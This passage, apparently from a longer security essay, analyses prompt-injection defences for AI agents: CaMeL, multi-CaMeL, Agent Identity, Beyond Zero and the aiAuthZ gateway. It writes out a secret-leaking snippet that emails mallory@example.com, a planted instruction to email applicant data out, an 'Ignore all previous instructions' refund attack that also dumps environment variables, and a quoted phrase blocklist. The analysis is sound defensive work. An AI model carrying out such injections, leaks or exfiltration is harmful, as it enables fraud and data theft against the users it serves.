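Researchers usually test these defences on *AgentDojo*, a benchmark with 35 attacker goals and 97 ordinary tasks involving email, Slack, banking and travel. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives CaMeL's completion rate as 67%, a figure from an early version of the CaMeL paper.

Others have since measured lower rates. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran an adapted version of CaMeL on the whole benchmark. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran it on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, with its policies on and off. They also tested their own agent, Randori. The banking results below are for the model GPT-5.2, and the attack figures leave out CaMeL runs that did not finish:

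| Test | System | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| *SecureClaw*, all tasks | CaMeL | 29 of 97 (30%) | 0 of 629 |
| Garby and colleagues, banking | CaMeL, policies off | 32 of 48 (67%) | 1 of 240 |
| Garby and colleagues, banking | CaMeL, policies on | 18 of 48 (38%) | 0 of 231 |
| Garby and colleagues, banking | Randori | 36 of 48 (75%) | 2 of 432 |

The people who ran these tests were proposing rival systems and may have put less effort into getting CaMeL to work well. But the banking results suggest that CaMeL completes fewer tasks because of its policies. Separating planning from reading stopped all but one of the attacks on its own, and turning on the policies stopped the last one but almost halved the number of completed tasks.

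Some of CaMeL's security comes from stopping early. *MetaPermit* (2026), which used the model MiniMax-M2.7 without adapting CaMeL to it, examined 5,581 runs in which CaMeL resisted the attack but did not complete the user's task. In 4,706 of them, CaMeL stopped after at most two tool calls. Stopping that early can prevent an attack, but so would refusing to start the task.

Better models reduce the drop in task completion that CaMeL causes, but they don't eliminate it. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include Shumailov from the original CaMeL team, tested CaMeL without policies on a set of industrial maintenance tasks. It lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest. Most failures occurred because the program had to be complete before the agent had seen any data. An ordinary agent that opens a file and finds it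 needs a second one can fetch it, but CaMeL can do so only if the program already provides for that case.

### Mistakes in the interpreter

CaMeL's guarantees depend on the interpreter labelling everything correctly. Garby and colleagues found several cases where it does not. One involves a program like this, in which `balance` is secret:

```
a = True
b = True
if balance > 10000: a = False
if a: b = False
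if b: send_email("mallory@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, the third line sets `a` to False and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `b` is still True and keeps its original public label. The last line contains nothing labeled secret, so the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is lower, `b` becomes False and Mallory gets no email. Either way, Mallory learns whether the balance is above 10,000. The labels don't capture this leak because the interpreter adds a label only when an assignment runs, and here the information comes from a skipped assignment.

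An honest model is unlikely to write such a roundabout program by accident. It could more easily make the mistake of inserting an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, which could make CaMeL treat it as trusted. CaMeL also retries failed programs in a loop outside the interpreter, where no labels apply. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest.

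Garby and colleagues responded by designing a small programming language, LLMbda, and proving that its labels prevent secret data from affecting public results, except through whether the program finishes. They checked the proof in Lean, and it covers the same interpreter that calls the model. Randori, which is written in LLMbda, can test and correct its program in an artificial copy of its environment before it has any contact with real data.

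Two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded across three models, both on the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Labels cannot settle this case, because the user did ask the agent to follow the file.

CaMeL failed differently on another banking task, which asked it to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With the policies off, the privileged model wrote a program that went through the file and called the tool named in each instruction. The model wrote the whole program before the file was read, as CaMeL requires, but the program was an interpreter for the file's instructions, so the attacker could use it to call the tools.

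### Several agents, and agents that use a screen

Protecting each agent in a group with CaMeL does not protect the group. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a coordinating agent to send Julie a Slack message summarizing some job applicants. One agent fetched the records from a database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The coordinator put the summary, including the planted instruction, into its request to a third agent, which sends notifications. That agent's privileged model treated the whole request as coming from its user, and wrote a program that sent both the Slack message and the email.

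Their extension, *multi-CaMeL*, gives agents separate channels for instructions and data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the receiving agent's privileged model cannot see the data. Averaged across the five models, the attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and 0% with multi-CaMeL.

Agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen are harder to protect, because the program must anticipate whatever might appear there. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), the privileged model wrote programs that averaged 213 lines and about 40 alternative branches, compared with 52 lines and about four branches for AgentDojo. The agents kept at most 57% of the performance of unprotected frontier models.

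Those branches give an attacker more options. A program for using the web will probably have a step that closes cookie notices. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's site. In this attack, which they call *branch steering*, the attacker uses false information to choose among the program's existing steps without adding a new one.

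In this respect, CaMeL makes an agent more like an ordinary service, where input can also choose among existing code paths but can't add new ones. But Google's engineers have reviewed the mail frontend's code paths before the frontend handles anyone's mail.

### Reviewed policies around an unreviewed plan

With a system like CaMeL, the mail team could put the interpreter, the tools and the policies through normal code review. BAB could then require the approved versions before letting the job run as the mail assistant. But a model wrote the program that sends Carol the agenda after Alice made her request, seconds before it ran, so by BAB's standards that program is unreviewed code running in production.

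Alice could read the program, which is only a few lines long, but most users would not want to, and they could hardly read a 213-line program.

A better reason to accept it is that the policies apply no matter who wrote the program. Garby and colleagues conclude from their proofs that even a fully compromised model can do only what the tools' policies allow, unless its program declares untrusted data to be trusted. In the terms Schneider and colleagues used in 2011, this trust comes from encapsulation rather than pedigree, as it does for the code Google runs under gVisor.

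The tool policies therefore have to be right. Tallam and Miller note that CaMeL needs a policy for every tool, and that a large company with hundreds of tools could end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules.

The condition about untrusted data is also a serious restriction. Randori's programs may *endorse* a value, which means declaring it trusted so that a payment can go ahead. Without this option, Randori could not pay a bill from a file. But the model that writes the program then also decides which outside data to trust, so a model again sets part of the policy. The model decides this before reading the data, so Bob's email cannot influence the decision.

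Policies also do not detect a permitted action that the user did not want. If Alice asks her assistant to archive her old newsletters and the privileged model writes a program that deletes them, the interpreter will run it, provided the policy lets the assistant delete mail. Dongol explicitly leaves the correctness of the planner out of the proofs. CaMeL also assumes that the request is trustworthy, but users sometimes paste in other people's text. If Alice includes a paragraph from Bob's email, the privileged model will read it as her own words.

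## What an agent's permissions are tied to, 2025 and 2026

Tool policies limit what an agent can do, but a company also has to decide which agents get which permissions. Google's own services get their permissions by running reviewed code. Google tied the permissions of its cloud customers' AI agents to where those agents run.

Hemrajani announced this scheme, called Agent Identity, in *What's new in IAM* at Google Cloud's 2026 conference. It was already generally available for Agent Runtime, a service that runs customers' agents. Each agent gets its own identity, which is a different type from the identities given to people and ordinary programs.

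### A name for the place where the agent runs

Suppose the mail team runs its assistant on Agent Runtime. Google Cloud creates a *resource* for it, which is a permanent entry with its own ID, and builds the agent's name from that ID. The names follow SPIFFE, an open standard for identifying programs. A shortened example might be:

`spiffe://example-company/.../reasoningEngines/mail-assistant`

Administrators grant permissions to this name. According to Google Cloud, the agent also receives a certificate for the name, which lasts 24 hours and renews automatically. To call a Google service, the agent requests an access token that is cryptographically bound to the certificate. If a thief copies the token and tries to use it on another machine, the request returns an error. Developers can switch this protection off, but Google Cloud's *Use Agent Identity with Agent Runtime* strongly discourages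 doing so.

An agent can act on its own authority or on a user's. Google's internal services make the same distinction with end-user tickets. When an agent acts for a user, the user first consents through OAuth, a standard way to let one program act for a user in another. A central vault stores the resulting credential. In some configurations, a gateway adds the credential to the agent's requests, so the agent never receives it. The logs show both the user and the agent when the agent acts for a user, and only the agent when it acts on its own authority.

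### What happens when the code changes

If the team deletes the assistant and deploys a replacement with the same name, code and configuration, the replacement gets a new resource ID and therefore a new identity. The old permissions don't apply to it, and an administrator has to grant them again.

By contrast, updating an agent keeps its identity. Google Cloud's *Manage revisions and traffic* explains that changing an agent's code or certain settings creates a *revision*, a fixed snapshot stored under the same resource. Google Cloud doesn't say outright that the identity carries over to the new revision, but this follows from the identity's name, which includes the resource's ID and not the revision's.

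In *Revisions and traffic splitting on Agent Runtime*, Dani shows how different two revisions of an agent can be. The first version of a research agent ran a quick web search and answered in about ten seconds, while the second started a research report that took ten minutes or more. Dani split the traffic evenly and asked the same question a dozen times. Seven requests went to the first version and five to the second, all through the same address and resource.

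In Google's sample code, the system prompt and the model's name are part of the agent's program, so changing either produces a new revision under the same agent name. The team can create the agent's identity and grant it permissions before writing any code.

The table compares this with BAB, assuming that the mail frontend has BAB's default policy:

| What the team does | Mail frontend under BAB | Mail assistant under Agent Identity |
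|---|---|---|
| Deploys a reviewed update | Keeps its identity | Keeps its identity |
| Deploys an unreviewed update | Borg refuses to start it | Keeps its identity |
| Deletes it and deploys the same code again | Keeps its identity | Gets a new identity |

A stable name is useful because an agent that lost its permissions whenever someone corrected a spelling mistake in its prompt would be hard to run. BAB also keeps names stable, but only for versions that pass its check, a condition that Agent Identity doesn't have. If Mallory is allowed to update the assistant, she can delete "Never send a message without the user's approval" from its prompt, and the new revision will have the same access to mail as the old one. A company could require a review before every deployment, but the certificate would not depend on that review.

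Google calls these identities "strongly attested". The attestation seems to cover where the agent runs, because neither the name nor the certificate, as Google describes them, identifies the agent's code, prompt or model.

### Beyond Zero: a decision for every action

An agent's name is a poor guide to what the agent will do, so much of the security has to come from checking its actions. Google Cloud customers can do some of this checking with fixed rules. According to Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes*, access policies that became generally available on 31 August 2026 can allow or deny a request based on the tool's name or whether the tool only reads data.

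Google has a more ambitious plan for its own company, which Valente and Zalewski (2026) describe in *Beyond Zero*. It extends BeyondCorp, Google's access system for employees. Valente and Zalewski argue that BeyondCorp was designed for people working at human speed and granted trust by application. An employee who could open an application could often reach a lot of data inside it, and an agent with the same permissions can read that data much faster. Beyond Zero therefore makes a separate access decision for each action on each resource, such as opening one document.

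These decisions have to be quick, so AI systems prepare much of the information in advance. They use personnel records, project assignments and past activity to work out what each person is supposed to be doing, and they classify documents by sensitivity. When a request arrives, the system applies fixed rules, which Valente and Zalewski call the "floor". A *reasoning engine* above these rules, made up of a group of AI systems, looks for unusual or risky behaviour. It can allow the action, deny it or issue a *challenge*, such as asking the user to touch a security key or explain the request. A slower analysis can examine a longer series of actions and lead to *containment*, which removes some or all of a person's access.

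Valente and Zalewski illustrate the process with an imaginary agent called SalesGenie, which has permission to read sales reports:

1. An employee gives SalesGenie a task, and it tries to open a highly sensitive strategy document in Google Drive.
2. BeyondCorp finds that the employee and the agent both have valid certificates and permission to read sales reports. It allows the access.
3. Beyond Zero also considers the employee's job and the document. The employee handles financial-services customers in the US Northeast, and has recently tried to reach other data unrelated to that work. Normally only the strategy and finance teams use the document.
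4. A rule requires a relevant work assignment for anything this confidential. The employee has none, so the system issues two challenges. The employee must confirm that they wanted the agent to open the document, and the team that owns it must approve.
5. The employee fails the challenges. The slower analysis finds signs that they have been trying to take data out of the company, and the system contains them.

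The employee's confirmation should stop an agent that has gone beyond its task, unless the employee approves the request without reading it. The owners' approval also guards against an employee who wants the document for a bad reason. Neither challenge depends on which model or prompt SalesGenie is using.

The rule in step 4 is fixed, but it relies on facts that AI helped prepare, so it would not apply if a model wrongly classified the strategy document as routine. The reasoning engine also needs to be trustworthy, and it is no easier to review than the agents it supervises. It can read an agent's prompts, plans and tool calls, which may contain text from an attacker, so it could also be vulnerable to prompt injection.

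If the engine can only add restrictions, an attacker who fools it must still satisfy the fixed rules. But Valente and Zalewski imagine letting the engine drop some controls, such as the request to touch a security key, when the risk seems low. A mistake would then remove a protection. A mistake in the other direction could lock out an innocent employee, and they expect people to review only a tiny percentage of containment decisions. Google is more cautious with BAB's daily check, since its published response to a violation is only a notification.

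There is little evidence yet of how well Beyond Zero works. Adkins and Ramamoorthy report in *Going Beyond Zero* (2026) that early internal versions have improved detection of access abuse and protection of intellectual property. They give no figures but promise further papers.

Google Cloud has offered customers a preview of something similar since June 2026. Its *Semantic governance overview* describes a language model that compares each proposed tool call with the user's request and with rules in plain English. One sample rule forbids automatic refunds above $75, so the model should block a refund for an $89 order. A language model may be useful for deciding whether an action matches what a user meant, but ordinary code is better for comparing 89 with 75 because it will get the answer right every time. Google Cloud recommends keeping conventional access controls underneath the model's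 checks.

### A $149 order and a $10,000 refund

*Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit* (Saboo and Dong, 2026) demonstrates several controls on a customer service agent. The agent reads a customer's message, writes a short program to work out any deductions, and records the refund in a database. An attacker with a damaged $149 order tells it to ignore its instructions, refund $10,000, and run a program that prints the host computer's environment variables, which often contain passwords and keys.

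A line in the system prompt could forbid refunds above the order's total, but Saboo and Dong assume that an attacker can trick the model. They add three protections outside it:

- The agent signs each change to the database with its own key, and the database checks the signature.
- Programs that the agent writes run under gVisor, without a network connection and for at most five seconds.
- A gateway checks messages and database commands against fixed rules.

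The sandbox deals with the second half of the attack. A program inside it cannot send secrets over the network, and as configured it doesn't receive the host's environment variables.

The signature does not stop the refund. If the model accepts the attacker's story, the agent creates a record for $10,000 and signs it. The signature is valid because the right agent wrote the record and nobody has altered it since. A signature would help if someone instead broke into the database and changed an existing refund from $149 to $10,000. The record would no longer match its signature, and a later audit would detect the change.

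The gateway has to stop the refund, and one of its rules does. The gateway also checks incoming messages against a list of phrases typical of an attack, but the list as printed in the article misses the article's own example. The attacker writes "Ignore all previous instructions" and "$10,000", while the list has "ignore previous instructions", some other variants of it, and "10,000.00".

The rule that works applies to database commands. It blocks any command that contains `update orders` but not the text `149.00`. The $10,000 refund doesn't contain that text, so the gateway blocks it. This is enough for a demonstration with one order, but the rule searches for characters and does not compare amounts. The printed code would treat other refunds as follows:

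| Refund the agent tries to record | Correct decision | What the gateway does |
|---|---|---|
| $149.00 on the $149 order | Allow | Allows it |
| $10,000.00 on the $149 order | Block | Blocks it |
| $9,149.00 on the $149 order, written `9149.00` | Block | Allows it |
| $134.10 on the $149 order, after a deduction | Allow | Blocks it |
| $149.00 on somebody's $20 order | Block | Allows it |

A real rule has to consult the order record. Let a be the requested refund, p the amount the customer paid for the order, and r the total already refunded on it. Ordinary code reads p and r from the database and allows the refund only if:

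a > 0 and r + a ≤ p

For the damaged order, p is 149 and r is 0. A request for $10,000 fails because 10,000 is more than 149, however persuasive the customer's message is. Without r in the rule, an attacker could request $149 repeatedly and collect $10,132 after 68 refunds. The system also has to confirm that this customer placed the order, using their login and not a claim in the message. It must check and record the refund in a single step, so that two simultaneous requests cannot both be checked against an r of 0.

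This rule still can't tell whether the order arrived damaged. A customer who lies about that can get back the full $149.

### Permission for a task

OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), a guide for companies that use agents, describes an action that a spending limit would not catch. An agent processing invoices notices that the company's subscription to a document-signing service is about to expire. To keep working, it tries to renew the subscription. The company may already have approved the vendor and the amount, but renewing means agreeing to a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do.

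OpenAI recommends treating an agent's identity as a combination of several things:

- a *bill of materials*, which lists the software behind the agent and gives evidence of where it came from
- a runtime identity, which shows which running program is acting
- the task, including who requested it and what it permits
- often, identifiers for the session and for the program making the request

The bill of materials resembles the provenance that BAB checks, and the runtime identity resembles Google Cloud's Agent Identity. Tying permissions to the task is what would prevent the agent from renewing a subscription without a new approval. When an employee asks the agent to process invoices, the system creates a token for that task, bound to the employee and the running agent. The agent exchanges the token for short-lived credentials, each for a particular resource and action.

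Someone still has to define the task well. "Process this month's invoices" may or may not include a late fee, and if the definition is too narrow, employees will get constant requests for approval. OpenAI does not specify how a company should compare the bill of materials with an approved version, and it reports no tests of the whole arrangement.

The guide recommends placing limits close to what they protect. For example, a payment service should enforce its own spending limit, so that the limit applies no matter which agent or tool sends the request. A company also has to be able to both stop an agent and cancel its credentials. OpenAI warns that credentials an agent has already passed to other services remain valid after the agent is stopped, and that cancelling a credential does not stop work in progress.

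### Moving the check off the agent's machine

Kodathala (2026), in *aiAuthZ*, built and tested a gateway that makes these decisions on a separate machine, where the agent cannot read or change its rules. Every user message carries a timestamp, a single-use number and a code made with that user's secret key. When the agent tries to use a tool, the gateway identifies the user who sent the latest verified message, then checks whether that user may use the tool and whether details such as the file or the recipient are acceptable.

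Kodathala gave 15 models eight attack scenarios. The 14 models that completed them all each refused between 38% and 100% of the attacks. The gateway blocked every dangerous call that the models made, and each decision took at most 0.03 milliseconds. Kodathala acknowledges that this is expected, because the rules prohibited the tools that the attacks needed. The result is still useful because it was the same for every model, so a company could know that the gateway would block those calls without knowing which model was running.

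A test on AgentDojo's banking tasks gives a better idea of the cost. Kodathala used 20 combinations of task and attack for each setup. *Spotlighting* is a defence that puts markers around untrusted text:

| Model | Defence | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | None | 0% | 100% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Spotlighting | 0% | 80% | 0% |
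| Claude Fable 5 | aiAuthZ | 0% | 80% | 0% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | None | 0% | 100% | 60% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | Spotlighting | 10% | 100% | 70% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | aiAuthZ | 0% | 80% | 40% |

The gateway blocked seven calls that would have served the attacker, including payments and two password changes. But no attack had succeeded without a defence either, so the gateway couldn't lower the attack success rate. It did lower the share of ordinary tasks that the agents completed, from 100% to 80%, because it allowed payments only to known recipients and so blocked a legitimate first payment to a new one. That single payment accounts for the whole fall, which suggests that the test had only about five ordinary tasks. With so few, the true effect on ordinary tasks could be considerably larger or smaller.

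In this test, the list of recipients blocked the attacks. Checking the user's identity made no difference because the injected instructions reached an agent working for a genuine user, which is another case of the confused deputy problem. Identity matters more when the attacker is a different person, such as a stranger in a shared chat who claims to be the agent's owner. In nine cases based on earlier incidents, the full gateway blocked every attack, while rules about the tools' inputs alone blocked four. In the other five, someone posed as the owner and used a tool that the owner was allowed to use.

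The gateway protects only the tools that go through it. When Kodathala tried it with two agent programs that still had their own tools for running commands and opening files, the model used those tools and never contacted the gateway. Like BAB, the gateway works only if nothing can bypass it. Kodathala's strongest remedy is to keep all passwords and keys on the gateway, so that an agent that bypasses it has no credentials.

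### Permitted actions that do harm

The best argument for checking an agent's actions is that the check works whatever caused the agent's error. A model might request a $10,000 refund because of a hidden backdoor, an instruction in a customer's message, an unapproved prompt or an ordinary mistake. The refund rule blocks the request in every case, and nobody needs to understand the model's weights. The rule is also a few lines of ordinary code, which a second engineer can review and BAB can protect.

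But a rule like this covers only the harm its author could describe in advance. Suppose the refund agent handles 1,000 claims a day on $149 orders, and 100 of them are false. The company tested the agent and found it rejects nearly all the false ones. If someone replaces its model with one that approves every claim, the company could lose up to $14,900 a day. Every refund would be within the limit and go to a real customer, and issuing refunds is the agent's task. A daily cap would reduce the loss, but would also block genuine refunds once the agent reached it.

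Actions that are harmless individually can also be harmful together, as Kodathala points out. An agent might have good reasons to read a confidential file and to send a message to a supplier, but not to put the file's contents in the message. CaMeL's labels can catch some of these cases by tracking where data came from. They can't catch harm that comes from the agent's judgement, as when the mail assistant reads only mail it is allowed to read but leaves an urgent message out of Alice's morning summary.

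In these cases the company depends on the model to do its job well. Its evidence that the model will do so comes from tests, which apply only to the version tested. Google Cloud can include the revision number in its logs, so the company could find out afterwards which refunds the replacement had approved. But it could not use Agent Identity to give only the tested revision permission to issue refunds, because both revisions have the same name.
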